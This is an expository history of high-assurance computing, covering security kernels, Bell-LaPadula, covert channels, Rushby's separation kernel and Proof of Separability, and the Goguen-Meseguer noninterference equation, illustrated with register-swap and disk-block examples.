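# Separation kernels and noninterference: isolating components in high-assurance systems

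## Security kernels and covert channels before 1981

A separation kernel is a small operating-system core that makes the programs sharing one computer behave as if each ran on its own machine, connected only in ways the designers have declared. Noninterference is the mathematical definition of that isolation. It requires that what one program does not change what another can observe. Both ideas date from the early 1980s and grew out of a decade of work, much of it for the United States military, on computers that held information at several classification levels and served people who weren't cleared for all of it.

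### Kernels and the demand for proof

An operating system is the software between a computer's hardware and its application programs. It supplies services that most programs need, such as opening a file or printing text, which programs request through system calls. The kernel, the operating system's innermost layer, runs directly on the hardware and controls the memory, processor and devices, so a flaw in it can expose everything on the machine.

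Around 1970 the US Air Force had no operating system that it trusted to keep users apart. It therefore cleared every user of a machine for the most secret information on it, or ran separate machines for separate work. The alternative was multilevel security, in which one machine holds information at several levels of secrecy and some of its users lack clearance for some of it. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, estimated that this could save 20 to 40 per cent of the cost of running the Air Force computers that handled classified data. Fences and guards do little to protect a multilevel machine, because the threat comes from people who have legitimate accounts and may be allowed to write and run programs.

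Commercial systems of the time offered no defence against that person. By 1972 every known "tiger team", a group that attacks a system to test it, had found a way in. Anderson added that a failed attack would have left the system's security unknown, because the outcome depends on the team's skill. Walker made the same point for the Department of Defense in 1980, writing in *The advent of trusted computer operating systems* that the absence of known flaws cannot prove that a system deserves trust, since there may always be another flaw.

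High assurance requires positive evidence that a system is secure, strong enough for uses in which failure is intolerable. *A Survey of Formal Models for Computer Security* (Landwehr, 1981) described the form this evidence was supposed to take. The designers write a mathematical model of what "secure" means for their system. They show that any system obeying the model satisfies the regulations that apply to it, and then that their own design obeys the model. If there is a gap in either step, the argument is incomplete even if the code is good.

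The model needs a counterpart in the machine, and Anderson's study proposed the reference monitor. It divides the system into subjects, which act (users and the programs running for them), and objects, which subjects act upon (files, devices, other programs). A table with a row for each subject and a column for each object records which kinds of access the subject has, such as reading or writing. The reference monitor checks every access against the table. The hardware and software that carry out the checks must be tamper-proof, impossible to bypass, and small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

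The requirements are harder to meet together than they look. Anderson's example was GCOS III, the operating system of a Honeywell mainframe. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but most of GCOS III ran with that check switched off, even while working on a user's behalf. If GCOS III is counted as the monitor during that work, then the monitor and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyze completely.

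A security kernel is a small core of software that implements the reference monitor, so that security does not depend on the rest of the operating system. Landwehr credits the idea to Roger Schell, the Air Force major who managed Anderson's study. Several projects tried to build one during the 1970s. The most relevant here is KSOS, the Kernelized Secure Operating System, which Ford Aerospace built for the Department of Defense on a PDP-11 minicomputer. KSOS offered programs the same interface as the UNIX operating system, but in early measurements it had about a tenth of the computing power of similar hardware running ordinary UNIX.

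### The Bell-LaPadula rules

A reference monitor enforces whatever its table contains. For military use, the table had to reflect the classification system, whose four levels are, in ascending order, unclassified, confidential, secret and top secret. Information may also belong to compartments, such as one for nuclear weapons, and a reader needs clearance for each of them. One classification dominates another if its level is at least as high and its set of compartments includes the other's. Some pairs are incomparable. For example, neither "secret, nuclear" nor "secret, NATO" dominates the other, so information should not pass between them in either direction.

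David Bell and Leonard LaPadula, working at the MITRE Corporation for the Air Force, turned this into the model that most later projects used. Two rules make up its core:

- No reading up: a subject may not read an object whose classification lies above the subject's clearance. The model's name for this rule is the simple security property.
- No writing down: a subject may not write to an object whose classification lies below the level at which the subject is currently working. This is the *-property, pronounced "star property".

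The first rule carries over from paper documents. The second has no close equivalent there, because it guards against programs that copy a user's data and pass it to somebody else. A Trojan horse is a program that does something useful for the person who runs it while leaking that person's data. Landwehr describes how one could defeat ADEPT-50, a time-sharing system of the late 1960s that ran in the Pentagon. ADEPT-50 stopped users from reading files above their level, but a Trojan horse run by a cleared user could copy secret text into an existing unclassified file, where anybody could read it. The rule against writing down blocks the copy whether or not the user knows about it. It also means that a cleared person has to work at the unclassified level to write an unclassified memo.

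Bell and LaPadula treated the computer as a machine that moves from one state to the next, and called a state secure if every access in progress obeys both rules. They then proved that no operation that can change the state, such as opening a file or granting access to another user, leads from a secure state to an insecure one. So if the machine starts in a secure state, every state it can reach is secure too.

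### Lampson's confinement problem

The proof covers accesses to objects. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) had already shown that information can also travel between programs that never touch a forbidden object. Lampson considered a customer who runs somebody else's program, called a service, on confidential data. The customer can limit what the service may read. The confinement problem is to stop the service from passing data it has legitimately received to the service's owner. Unlike a wrong answer, such a leak usually leaves the customer with no evidence.

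Access rules can stop some of the leaks on Lampson's list. For example, the service could write the data into a file that the service's owner can read, or send the owner a message. Other leaks are much less obvious, and two of them became the standard examples of two kinds of channel.

A storage channel passes information through stored state that one program can alter and another can examine. Lampson's example uses a file lock. Many systems prevent one program from writing a file while another is reading it. To send a 1, the service opens an agreed file for reading, and to send a 0 it leaves the file closed. The owner's program then tries to open the same file for writing. If the system reports that the file is in use, the bit is 1. Two more files serve as clocks, so that the service knows when the owner's program has taken each bit. Both Bell-LaPadula rules permit this when the service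 works at the secret level and the file and the owner's program are unclassified, because the service only reads down and the owner's program writes at its own level.

A timing channel passes information through how long operations take. The service can vary its paging rate, which is how often it makes the system move blocks of data between main memory and disk. Heavy paging slows the whole machine, and a program running at the same time can detect the delay in its own work. Other users' activity adds noise, but Lampson pointed out that a suitable code still gets the message through reliably, though perhaps very slowly, as long as the paging has any effect at all on the other program.

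Lampson used "covert" only for channels such as the load on the system, and put storage in a separate category. In the later usage that Millen describes in *20 Years of Covert Channel Modeling and Analysis*, covert channels include both storage and timing channels. The boundary between the two is not sharp, and Millen mentions a channel through the position of a disk arm that specialists could not agree how to classify.

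Lampson thought a trustworthy operating system could block these paths. It would have to find every kind of storage that a confined program can affect, and then control the program's influence on everything else, for instance by slowing it down or adding needless disk accesses until the load it produced matched what the customer had specified. He accepted that this might take a lot of resources and suggested limiting the capacity of the channels as a less demanding alternative. He also admitted that no rigorous method was likely to find every channel in a system of even moderate complexity, which is a more serious difficulty for anyone who wants a proof. His argument rests on a list of the leaks he had been able to think of.

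Millen encountered the problem while working on a prototype security kernel at MITRE. He had just finished proving that the kernel satisfied the Bell-LaPadula model when its designer explained that a high-level process could signal to a lower one by using up the disk quota, since the lower process could detect that the space was gone. Such a proof can be correct even though the channel exists. A call from a high-level process can change the kernel's internal variables, and this can change the result of a later call from a low-level process. As Landwehr explains, the original axioms did not account for the information conveyed by refusing a request. By his account, Bell and LaPadula's final rules contain no storage channels, but timing channels remain possible. These are easy to overlook in this style of model because the modeled machine moves between states instantaneously, leaving no durations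 to observe.

A spy with a high clearance could simply memorise a document and so, as *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* argues, has no need of covert channels. The usual sender is a Trojan horse that somebody with a low clearance has planted and a more highly cleared user runs in good faith. Even a channel that leaks only a few bits at a time is enough for some secrets. A 512-bit encryption key, an example that Millen uses, would take less than nine minutes to leak at one bit per second.

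Covert channels were one reason people were dissatisfied with access rules, and in 1982 noninterference would replace those rules with a condition on what each party can observe. Kernel builders had a second problem with the rules, which prohibited operations that a working system needed, even where they prevented every leak they were meant to prevent.

### Trusted processes

Rushby (1981), in *Design and Verification of Secure Systems*, illustrates the second problem with a printer spooler, the program that keeps print jobs on disk until the printer is free. If the spooler and all its files sit at the highest level, users at lower levels cannot look at their own queued files, even to check a job's progress, because that would be reading up. Designers therefore usually left each file at its owner's level and ran the spooler at the highest level, from which it could read them all. But the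 spooler then cannot delete a file after printing it, because deletion alters something at a lower level, which the *-property forbids. Used files therefore pile up on the disk.

The rule prevents a real leak, because a top-secret program that could choose which unclassified files to delete could use those choices to send a message to anybody watching the directory. A properly written spooler does not do this, so the designers made it a trusted process, a program that the kernel allows to break the *-property. Bell and LaPadula had provided for such exceptions in their model. In KSOS, the exceptions also included programs that back up and restore the disk, and parts of the software for a communications network.

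Each exception weakens the original case for a security kernel, which was that one could verify the kernel and ignore everything else. Anderson's 1972 study had already concluded that any program for which the system suspends the checks is part of the security mechanism, and must be as tamper-proof and as open to complete analysis as the monitor itself. Verification therefore had to cover the kernel and all its trusted processes.

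More effort would not have been enough to do this, because nobody had stated what to verify. For ordinary programs, the kernel's task was clearly to enforce the two rules. For the spooler, the model recorded only which rule it might break, not when breaking it was safe, and Landwehr found little guidance in the model on which processes deserved trust. Researchers at SRI International prepared a version of the model for KSOS that narrowed the exemption, so that a function could be allowed to write down but still have to obey the rule on reading up. This limits the damage but does not define correct behaviour. For example, a secure printing service has to put the right classification on each job's header page and must not print part of one job inside another, and neither requirement follows from the Bell-LaPadula rules. There was also no theory of how to combine proofs about a trusted process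 with proofs about the kernel to show that the whole system was secure. Rushby concluded that "we do not know what it is that we have to prove", and he saw no real justification for calling such systems verified.

The ACCAT Guard posed a more basic problem than the spooler, which could pass for an awkward detail in a general-purpose computer. The Guard exchanged messages between a highly classified computer and a less classified one. Messages going up passed freely, while a security officer viewed those going down on a screen and decided whether to declassify and release them. The Guard's builders based it on the KSOS kernel, which permits flow only upwards, so every downward message had to go through trusted processes designed to get round the kernel's main rule. Rushby doubted that the kernel had contributed anything to the Guard's security, and he quoted a report by Landwehr that verifying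 the trusted processes had used far more resources than planned.

The KSOS developers blamed this on a mismatch between an idealised policy and the needs of real users. Landwehr expected work on models of trusted processes within the Bell-LaPadula framework to continue, and also mentioned the option of a separate security model for each application. The kernel of UCLA's Data Secure UNIX already left policy to a separate program and enforced only the permissions that program recorded. This removed the fixed rule from the kernel, but the underlying model covered only direct access and could not represent leaks through covert channels.

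Rushby thought it was a mistake for a kernel to impose one policy on every component of a system, because components such as a spooler and a guard each need their own requirements. He proposed removing the policy from the kernel, so that it would only keep components apart, and called this design a separation kernel.

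## Rushby's separation kernel, 1981 to 1984

Rushby's case for the separation kernel starts with a system that has no kernel. Each user of a multilevel system gets a private computer in a separate room, and a single cable connects each computer to a shared file-server. The computers are otherwise physically separate, so information can pass between users with different clearances only through a file. Rushby argued that the file-server is therefore the only component that has to be trusted. It runs one fixed program and no user's code, so it needs no operating system, and verifying it means showing that this program obeys the multilevel rules.

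Designers add other shared services in the same way. The print spooler, which KSOS had to run as a trusted process, becomes a printer-server with its own machine and cables. Deleting printed files had required an exemption from the *-property. The file-server now provides deletion as a specific service to the printer-server, and the designers can state exactly what that service does.

Rushby expected the objection that nobody can study such components separately, because the printer-server relies on the file-server, and both rely on an authentication service for each logged-in user's identity and clearance. He replied that a conventional kernelised system has the same dependencies but makes them harder to see. The comparison is fair, but the designer still has to do the hardest part of the work, which is to find a requirement for each component so that the components together enforce the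 policy of the whole system. Rushby described this task but offered no general procedure for it.

### The network encryption device

His main example was a more specialised system, a device that sits between a host computer and a network and encrypts what the host sends. User data must never reach the network as cleartext, meaning in unencrypted form. The device cannot simply encrypt everything, however, because the network needs to read the header of each packet in order to deliver it. Some information therefore has to travel around the encryption. The design has four components:

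- The red component communicates with the host and handles user data in cleartext.
- The crypto is a hardware unit that encrypts the data it receives from the red component and passes the result to the black component.
- The black component communicates with the network.
- The censor sits on the bypass, a second line from red to black that carries packet headers in cleartext.

The red component's software was too large and complex to verify, so the designers had to assume it might send user data over the bypass. The censor applies rigid checks to everything on the bypass and lets through only what looks like a legitimate exchange of headers. It cannot stop the red component from encoding some data in its choice of legitimate-looking headers. Rushby claimed that a fairly simple censor could reduce the capacity for this to an acceptable level, but he gave no figure.

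Information may flow from red to black only through the crypto or the censor. The classification rules of the 1970s cannot express this requirement, because if they allow information to flow from red to the censor and from the censor to black, they also allow it to flow directly from red to black. Later work on flow through an intermediary produced a formal policy for such cases. With four separate boxes, the requirement is easy to state and to check, since an inspector can look at the cables. The censor is then the only software in the device that performs a security-critical task.

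*Verification of Secure Systems*, a longer report by Rushby (1981), points out a risk in this design. If the censor checks a message in storage that the red component can also write to, and then copies the message to black, red could replace the message between the check and the copy. The censor can prevent this by reading each message only once. Alternatively, the mechanism connecting red and the censor can guarantee a buffer to which only red adds messages and from which only the censor removes them. The proof about the censor then assumes this guarantee, which has to be proved separately.

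### One processor in place of several machines

Building one encryption device from four computers is expensive. When the components are small, running them all on one processor costs less, and Rushby's argument brings back a kernel only at this point. The kernel's only task is to reproduce the separate machines and cables so faithfully that no component can distinguish the shared machine from a machine of its own. If it succeeds, the shared version should be as secure as the distributed one. The kernel does not refer to the policy of the system as a whole, and the censor and the file-server need no special privileges from it.

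Each component runs in a partition, which Rushby called a "regime". Partitions resemble the virtual machines that IBM's VM/370 already provided, which were simulated copies of the underlying computer. A separation kernel must provide communication channels between some of its partitions, but the partitions don't have to be exact copies of the computer.

Rushby illustrated the division of labour with an office. Workers sit in sealed rooms and exchange files through a clerk, who refuses requests that break the rules. When money runs short, the company can afford to heat only one room. Anyone in an unheated room falls unconscious, so a caretaker moves people in and out of the heated room in turn and puts each person's furniture and papers back exactly as they were. Both the clerk and the caretaker must do their jobs properly, but the clerk's job follows from the purpose of the office, while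 the caretaker's exists only because heated rooms are scarce. Rushby called the clerk's job the policy problem and the caretaker's the sharing problem, and thought it a grave design error to give both to one person. In a computer, the trusted components play the clerk and the separation kernel plays the caretaker.

Rushby did not present the idea as entirely new. Anderson had proposed virtual machines for security in 1974, and in the same year Gerald Popek, who worked on secure operating systems, described a kernel whose only job would be to isolate simple processes, with the file system running inside one of them. Rushby thought his own version had a sounder basis because it came with a method of proof.

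There was also a working example. The Royal Signals and Radar Establishment at Malvern, a British defence laboratory, had built the Secure User Environment, or SUE, to support applications like the encryption device. It ran on a PDP-11/34 minicomputer and was in use on the laboratory's experimental packet-switched network before Rushby worked out the theory. The kernel took up about 5K words of memory, including its stack and data. It was this small because its designers had left out most of what an operating system does:

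- Each partition permanently occupies a fixed area of memory and runs a fixed program, so the SUE has no virtual memory to manage.
- A partition keeps the processor until it gives it up voluntarily by calling an operation named SWAP, and control then passes to the next partition in a fixed rotation. The SUE does no other scheduling.
- The system excludes direct memory access, by which a device reads and writes main memory on its own. On a PDP-11 such transfers use absolute addresses and so evade the hardware's memory protection. Special-purpose hardware made up for the lost speed.
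- Each device belongs permanently to one partition. A PDP-11 program controls a device by reading and writing particular memory addresses, so the hardware that protects memory also protects the devices. The SUE only receives their interrupts, the signals with which devices demand attention, and passes them to the right partition.

Because handover is voluntary, a faulty or malicious component can stop all the others by never calling SWAP. Rushby accepted this because the whole machine served one function, so such a stoppage was a reliability problem rather than a security problem.

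### Proof of Separability

Rushby's method of proof, which he called Proof of Separability, compares the real machine that all the partitions share with an imaginary private machine for each partition. The kernel is secure if every partition's view of the shared machine always matches the state of its own private machine. Rushby reduced the method to six conditions.

The conditions need some notation. Let s and s′ be states of the shared machine, i and i′ inputs to it, and op one of its operations. Rushby gives each partition a colour, c. COLOUR(s) is the partition for which the machine is working in state s, and NEXTOP(s) is the operation that it executes next. INPUT(s, i) is the state that results when input i arrives in state s, and OUTPUT(s) is what the devices can observe in state s. Inputs and outputs consist of separate parts for the different partitions, and EXTRACT(c, i) picks out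 the part that belongs to c. Finally, Φ(c, s) is c's view of state s, which is a state of c's private machine, and ABOP(c, op) is the operation on the private machine that corresponds to op. For every choice of these, the following must hold:

1. COLOUR(s) = c ⇒ Φ(c, op(s)) = ABOP(c, op)(Φ(c, s)). When the machine executes an operation for c, c's view changes exactly as it would on the private machine.
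2. COLOUR(s) ≠ c ⇒ Φ(c, op(s)) = Φ(c, s). When the machine executes an operation for another partition, c's view does not change.
3. Φ(c, s) = Φ(c, s′) ⇒ Φ(c, INPUT(s, i)) = Φ(c, INPUT(s′, i)). If two states look the same to c, they still look the same to c after the same input has arrived.
4. EXTRACT(c, i) = EXTRACT(c, i′) ⇒ Φ(c, INPUT(s, i)) = Φ(c, INPUT(s, i′)). Only c's own part of an input can affect c's view.
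5. Φ(c, s) = Φ(c, s′) ⇒ EXTRACT(c, OUTPUT(s)) = EXTRACT(c, OUTPUT(s′)). If two states look the same to c, c's devices receive the same output in both.
6. COLOUR(s) = COLOUR(s′) = c and Φ(c, s) = Φ(c, s′) ⇒ NEXTOP(s) = NEXTOP(s′). The choice of the next operation for c depends only on c's view.

The first two conditions contain the main idea, but on their own they exclude no system, because each private machine could be given a single state that never changes. Condition 5 rules this out by tying c's view to real output, so that if the view never changed, c's output could never change either. Conditions 3 and 4 deal with devices, which can alter the machine's state at any moment, and condition 6 deals with the order in which the machine executes instructions. Rushby thought these matters especially important because attacks on conventional systems had so often succeeded through input, output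 and interrupts.

In *Proof of Separability*, Rushby (1982) set out to show that these were the right conditions. He started from the requirement that the results each user sees must depend only on that user's own input, and then weakened it twice. The first change ignores how long each output value lasts, so the definition treats an output of 1, 1, 2, 2, 2, 3 as 1, 2, 3. The second allows one run of the machine to stop early while another continues, as long as the two agree up to that point. Without these changes, the definition would have ruled out timing channels and denial of service, which Rushby thought a simple kernel could not prevent.

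A kernel can therefore satisfy all six conditions and still leak information through timing. In a system like the SUE, a partition can signal by varying how long it holds the processor. Rushby left such channels to ad hoc measures that add noise or reduce their capacity.

Rushby also pointed out a gap in his derivation. He proved that his conditions guarantee isolation for a machine that receives all its input at the start. Real devices deliver input while the machine is running, so he replaced one condition with two (3 and 4 above) to cover them. He could not derive the new set from a simple definition of security, so he asserted it based on its similarity to the set he had proved.

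### Swapping one register

SWAP is a good test of the method because it has to handle two partitions' data at once. A processor has only one set of registers, which hold the values it is working on. When the RED partition gives up the processor, the kernel copies RED's register values to a save area and reloads the values it saved earlier for BLACK.

For example, two partitions, RED and BLACK, might share a machine with one register. RED is active and the register holds 7. BLACK's save area holds 4, and RED's save area holds an old value, 0. A partition's view of the register is the register itself while the partition is active, and its save area while it waits.

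| | Register | RED's save area | BLACK's save area | RED's view | BLACK's view |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before the swap, RED active | 7 | 0 | 4 | 7 | 4 |
| After a correct swap, BLACK active | 4 | 7 | 4 | 7 | 4 |
| After a swap without the reload, BLACK active | 7 | 7 | 4 | 7 | 7 |

The correct swap reads a value belonging to each partition but leaves both views unchanged, so it satisfies conditions 1 and 2. Condition 1 requires RED's view to stay at 7 because SWAP does nothing on RED's private machine. Condition 2 requires BLACK's view to stay at 4 because the machine executed SWAP for RED.

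If the programmer forgets the reload, RED's view is still 7, so condition 1 holds. But an operation executed for RED has changed BLACK's view from 4 to 7, which is RED's value, and this violates condition 2. If the programmer forgets the save instead, RED's view changes from 7 to the old value 0, and condition 1 fails.

Neither of the two established methods of verifying kernels gave the right results for a separation kernel. The first, access control verification, proves that programs access only the memory they are allowed to access. Rushby built a toy kernel and sketched such a proof for it. The proof remained valid even after he deleted the steps in SWAP that save and reload the registers, because the rules about memory blocks don't cover registers.

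The second method, information flow analysis, errs in the opposite direction. It gives every variable a colour and rejects any operation whose text could let information move between variables of different colours. An operation that runs for RED may alter only RED variables. SWAP has to break this rule, since it runs for RED and puts BLACK's saved value into the register. The analysis also rejects the faulty version, in which the register keeps its contents while its colour changes from RED to BLACK. It checks only colours, not values, so it cannot distinguish this version from a correct SWAP, which returns to BLACK exactly what the kernel had saved for it.

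People who used flow analysis on kernels had an answer to this. They applied the analysis to a high-level specification in which every partition has its own set of registers, and left it to a second proof to show that the code implements the specification. Rushby objected that this left nearly everything that needed proving to the second proof, which projects skipped in practice. The contract for KSOS, for example, asked only for "illustrative" proofs of the code. He also showed that, for a kernel that isolates its partitions, splitting the second proof up by partition would reduce it to proving conditions 1 and 2. The new part of Proof of Separability is therefore the other four conditions, on devices and the order of instructions, which the model behind flow analysis could not express.

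SWAP also shows why checking operations one at a time is not enough. A variant of SWAP could set the registers to zero at every handover instead of restoring them. A kernel that offers only this variant is secure, because each partition always finds zeros when it resumes, but a kernel that offers both versions is insecure, because RED can choose between them and BLACK can tell from its registers which one RED chose. Proof of Separability handles this correctly, because a suitable definition of BLACK's view exists for either operation alone, but no single definition satisfies the conditions for both.

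Flow analysis did find a leak in the first version of Rushby's toy kernel. Partitions could request particular blocks of memory by number, so one could signal to another by taking and releasing block 0. Letting them request only an unspecified free block doesn't help, because one partition can still use up the supply. Making a partition wait until a block becomes free turns the storage channel into a timing channel. Rushby concluded that any finite resource that partitions share on demand causes this kind of problem, unless each partition has a quota and the system can meet all the quotas at once. The SUE's fixed memory areas satisfy this requirement. He continued to recommend flow analysis for trusted components such as the file-server, which are ordinary programs and do not have to manage the processor's registers for other programs.

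### Cutting the wires

All six conditions concern complete isolation, but a kernel for the encryption device has to provide channels. Rushby adapted the method by returning to the physical picture of four boxes connected by cables. If cutting every declared cable leaves the boxes completely isolated, there was no undeclared cable.

In software, a channel is ultimately a shared variable that the sender can write and the receiver can read. To cut it, the verifier gives the two ends different names. Suppose that partition 0 may send to partition 1 through a variable X, using an operation WRITE that copies a register into X and an operation READ that copies X into a register. The verifier replaces X by X1 in READ and by X2 in WRITE, so what partition 0 writes no longer reaches partition 1 through this channel. Rushby argued that if the altered system passes Proof of Separability, X was the only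 channel in the original. The verifier can then establish the channel's direction by inspecting the two operations, because only partition 0 can execute WRITE and only partition 1 can execute READ.

Rushby admitted that some readers might find the argument specious, since it proves something about one system and draws a conclusion about another. He answered that the two systems differ only in the names of a few variables, so one can completely understand the consequences of the difference.

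Rushby later reported in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies* (1992) that the approach had "recently been shown to be subtly flawed". He cited another researcher's paper for this result but did not explain the flaw. He wrote that the basic method for proving complete isolation had survived fairly intensive scrutiny with only minor corrections.

An inference of this kind could go wrong because cutting a channel changes the values that can arrive at the receiving end. Suppose a kernel has a hidden path that opens only after partition 1 has received a certain message through X. In the cut system that message never arrives, so the path never opens and the partitions behave as if isolated. A proof that covers every combination of values the variables could take would still reveal the path, but a proof restricted to the states the cut system can reach would not.

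In 1982, Rushby had suggested a different way to permit a channel. If RED may send to BLACK using WRITE, the verifier drops condition 2 for that case, so a WRITE executed for RED may change BLACK's view. Rushby called this ad hoc. It also does not restrict how WRITE may change BLACK's view, so the verifier must separately show that WRITE delivers RED's message and does nothing else. Rushby hoped that new work by Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer on describing security policies, which introduced noninterference, might provide a formal basis.

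### Separation and mediation

In *A Distributed Secure System* (1983), Rushby and Randell applied the same principles to a general-purpose system made of many computers. They distinguished two tasks that earlier designs had given to a single security kernel. Separation keeps parties with different classifications apart, and mediation controls what may pass between them. Once separation is a task in its own right, a kernel is only one of several ways to achieve it:

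- Physical separation gives each party its own machine.
- Temporal separation lets parties use the same machine at different times, provided that it retains nothing in between.
- Cryptographic separation lets them share a network or a disk under different encryption keys.
- Logical separation uses a separation kernel on a shared processor.

Their design used all four. Each untrusted, ordinary UNIX computer handled a single classification, and a small trustworthy unit connected it to the local network. The unit encrypted everything its computer sent, using a key that depended on the classification. If a secret machine sent a message to an unclassified one, the checksum would fail because the receiving unit held a different key, and that unit would discard the message. Inside each unit, a separation kernel kept cleartext apart from encrypted data, as in the encryption device.

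This isolates the classifications completely, whereas a multilevel system should let information move upwards. Rushby and Randell therefore added a trusted file store to mediate between the machines that the units keep separate. A secret machine deposits a file there, and a top-secret machine can later request a copy without revealing the request to the secret machine. Rushby and Randell decided against also giving top-secret units the secret key, which would have let them receive messages from below, because reliable communication requires acknowledgements, and these would carry information down. They expected the UNIX machines to run at full speed under their design, but they were still building the prototype when they wrote.

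In *A Trusted Computing Base for Embedded Systems* (1984), Rushby arranged these ideas in layers for computers dedicated to a single application. The bottom layer provides the partitions, which he now called domains, and the channels between them. The middle layer consists of resource managers, such as a file system or the software that runs a communications line, each in one or more partitions of its own. The top layer is the application.

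Mediation can happen in two places in this design. In simple systems, the fixed layout of the channels is enough, much as a building can keep visitors away from a room by having no corridor that leads there. In other systems, something has to check each request as it arrives, and Rushby wanted a separate check for each kind of resource, in the component that manages it. He reasoned that most resource managers need to be trusted anyway, although a single central check might seem enough because every request either reads or writes something. He used another office to explain why these managers need to be trusted.

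A filing clerk looks after a vault of unclassified folders and keeps a record of where each one is. Clerks with secret clearance may fetch folders from the vault, because reading down is permitted. Suppose the vault contains 26 folders of different sizes, and one of these clerks makes six permitted trips to fetch the 5th, 14th, 9th, 7th, 13th and 1st smallest. These numbers spell ENIGMA when read as positions in the alphabet, and the filing clerk can write this secret word down and put it in an unclassified folder. A manager that serves several levels and keeps a record of past requests can leak information this way even if something else checks every request against the rules.

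Rushby estimated that the separation kernel for such a system should need no more than a couple of hundred machine instructions. Each operation would be short enough to run with interrupts off, so a verifier could treat the kernel as a single sequential program. He recommended writing it in assembly language, the symbolic form of the processor's instructions. He thought a high-level language would not make verification easier, because the meaning of the code lies in its effect on the hardware. The statement "x := 0" normally stores a zero, but if x is the register that controls the processor's mode, the language's rules are almost no help in predicting what happens next.

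The trusted computing base consists of all the mechanisms on which a system's security depends. In this design, it includes the kernel and every partition in the middle or top layer that performs a trusted function. Even with a kernel of two hundred instructions, the trusted computing base can be large if the file system and other managers contain a lot of trusted code, and Rushby advised designers to minimize that code too. For example, he suggested dividing a disk into small separate disks and building the secure file system on top of them.

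## The definition of noninterference, 1982 to 1992

By 1982 the literature contained many security models, but Goguen and Meseguer objected in *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982) that nobody had explained what a security model was. They proposed distinguishing a security policy, which states what a system has to achieve, from a model, which describes what the system does. Verifying the system means proving that the model satisfies the policy. The Bell-LaPadula rules blur this distinction because they specify how a reference monitor treats reads and writes but not what those rules are supposed to accomplish.

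Goguen and Meseguer define a policy as a set of noninterference assertions. Each assertion means that one group of users cannot use certain commands to affect what another group sees. Multilevel security, for example, requires that users at any level have no effect on what users at lower levels see. A policy that only the security officer may change permissions becomes the assertion that the commands for changing permissions have no visible effect when anybody else issues them. Complete isolation, which Rushby wanted to prove for separation kernels, requires that a group have no effect on what other users see and that other users have no effect on what the group sees.

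None of these assertions refers to a file or an access table. The assertions cover file locks, disk quotas and error messages if these change what somebody sees. Goguen and Meseguer started from the influences that the policy forbids. They contrasted this with information flow analysis, which starts from everything that might influence something else, follows the chains of influence, and finds many flows that cannot actually occur.

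They also avoided trusted processes, because they thought it unnecessarily dangerous to admit programs that may do anything to the system. They wanted designers to write a precise policy for how each such program interacts with the rest of the system, and then verify it. Their approach does not cover user authentication, fault tolerance, or inferring secret facts by combining permitted ones.

### Purge and the security equation

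The 1982 model includes commands that change users' permissions, and assertions that hold only under certain conditions. In his 1992 report, Rushby presented the core of the definition for policies that stay fixed, in simpler notation. His machine has a set of states, one of which is the initial state s₀, and a set of actions. Two functions describe its behaviour:

- step(s, a) is the state that follows when the machine performs action a in state s.
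- output(s, a) is the result that action a returns in state s.

Each action a belongs to a domain, dom(a). A domain is a party in the policy, such as a user, a partition or everyone with the same clearance. The flow policy is a relation between domains, and u ⇝ v means that u may influence v directly. Every domain may influence itself.

Let α be a sequence of actions and Λ the empty sequence. The state that the machine reaches from s by performing all of α in order is run(s, α). The purge function deletes from α every action whose domain must not influence v. It works through the sequence one action at a time:

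- purge(Λ, v) = Λ.
- purge(a · α, v) = a · purge(α, v) if dom(a) ⇝ v. The action stays.
- purge(a · α, v) = purge(α, v) otherwise. The action disappears.

Finally, test(α, a) stands for output(run(s₀, α), a), the result of performing a after the sequence α. A system is secure if the following equation holds for every sequence α and every action a:

test(α, a) = test(purge(α, dom(a)), a)

Rushby described the final action a as an experiment. A domain performs a and examines the result to learn about what happened earlier. If the result differs from what it would have been without the forbidden actions, one of those actions has interfered with the domain. He found that letting the domain examine all the outputs it had legitimately received along the way gives an equivalent definition.

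The equation covers whole sequences because an action's effect may take time to appear. Gligor (1993), in *A Guide to Understanding Covert Channel Analysis of Trusted Systems*, gives the example of a machine that reports each of one process's inputs to another process after a delay. The next output reveals nothing about that input, but the channel works as well as it would without the delay. Gligor wrote the guide for the US National Computer Security Center, which evaluated commercial systems for the Department of Defense.

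The definition assumes that the initial state contains no sensitive information and that users learn things only through outputs, according to Purdue University's lecture notes *Noninterference and Nondeducibility*. If a secret file is already on the disk in s₀ and any user can print it, the equation still holds, because purging removes only actions, and no action put the file there. To expose the leak, the model has to start with an empty disk and treat writing the file as an action by a highly cleared user. The equation also cannot detect a timing channel if the model's outputs don't include how long an action takes.

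Mardziel (2007) criticised the use of purging. Deleting actions produces a different run of the machine, which may pass through quite different states. The remaining actions could be the end of a procedure without its beginning, and the modeller has to define what the machine does in that case. Every action therefore needs a result in every state, which makes it awkward to model systems in which some sequences cannot happen.

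### Three free disk blocks

Suppose two domains, High and Low, share a disk with three free blocks. Low may influence High, but High must not influence Low. Each domain has one action, a request for a block, written H for High and L for Low. If a block is free, the system allocates it and returns "ok". Otherwise it returns "full".

If High takes all three blocks, Low's next request returns "full". Purging High's actions leaves an empty sequence, so Low's request then reaches an untouched disk and returns "ok". In symbols, test(HHH, L) = full, but test(purge(HHH, Low), L) = test(Λ, L) = ok. The security equation requires these two results to be equal, so the system is insecure.

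This is a storage channel. If the system has an operation for releasing blocks, High can send one bit after another by taking all the blocks for a 1 and none for a 0. Low requests a block, reads the bit from the reply, and gives back any block it received. Loepere (1984) describes the same method in *Covert Channel Analysis*, a bulletin for developers of the Multics time-sharing operating system. Loepere considered the exhaustion of shared resources by far the most common type of covert channel.

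He proposed the same remedy Rushby had given for memory blocks, which was to give each process a quota that the system can always meet. In the example, High's quota might be two blocks and Low's one. The table compares the replies to Low's next request in both designs, with and without High's earlier actions.

| Actions so far | After purging for Low | Shared blocks, actual reply | Shared blocks, reply after purge | Quotas, actual reply | Quotas, reply after purge |
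|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| HHH | Λ | full | ok | ok | ok |
| HH | Λ | ok | ok | ok | ok |
| HLL | LL | full | ok | full | full |

With shared blocks, Low can detect High's activity even when High doesn't fill the disk. In the last row, High takes one block, and Low detects this by asking for three. With quotas, the reply Low gets depends only on how many blocks Low has already received, so purging High's actions never changes it, but the system can refuse Low a block while High's two blocks lie unused. Gligor noted that dividing resources this way is not always possible, because it can reduce performance.

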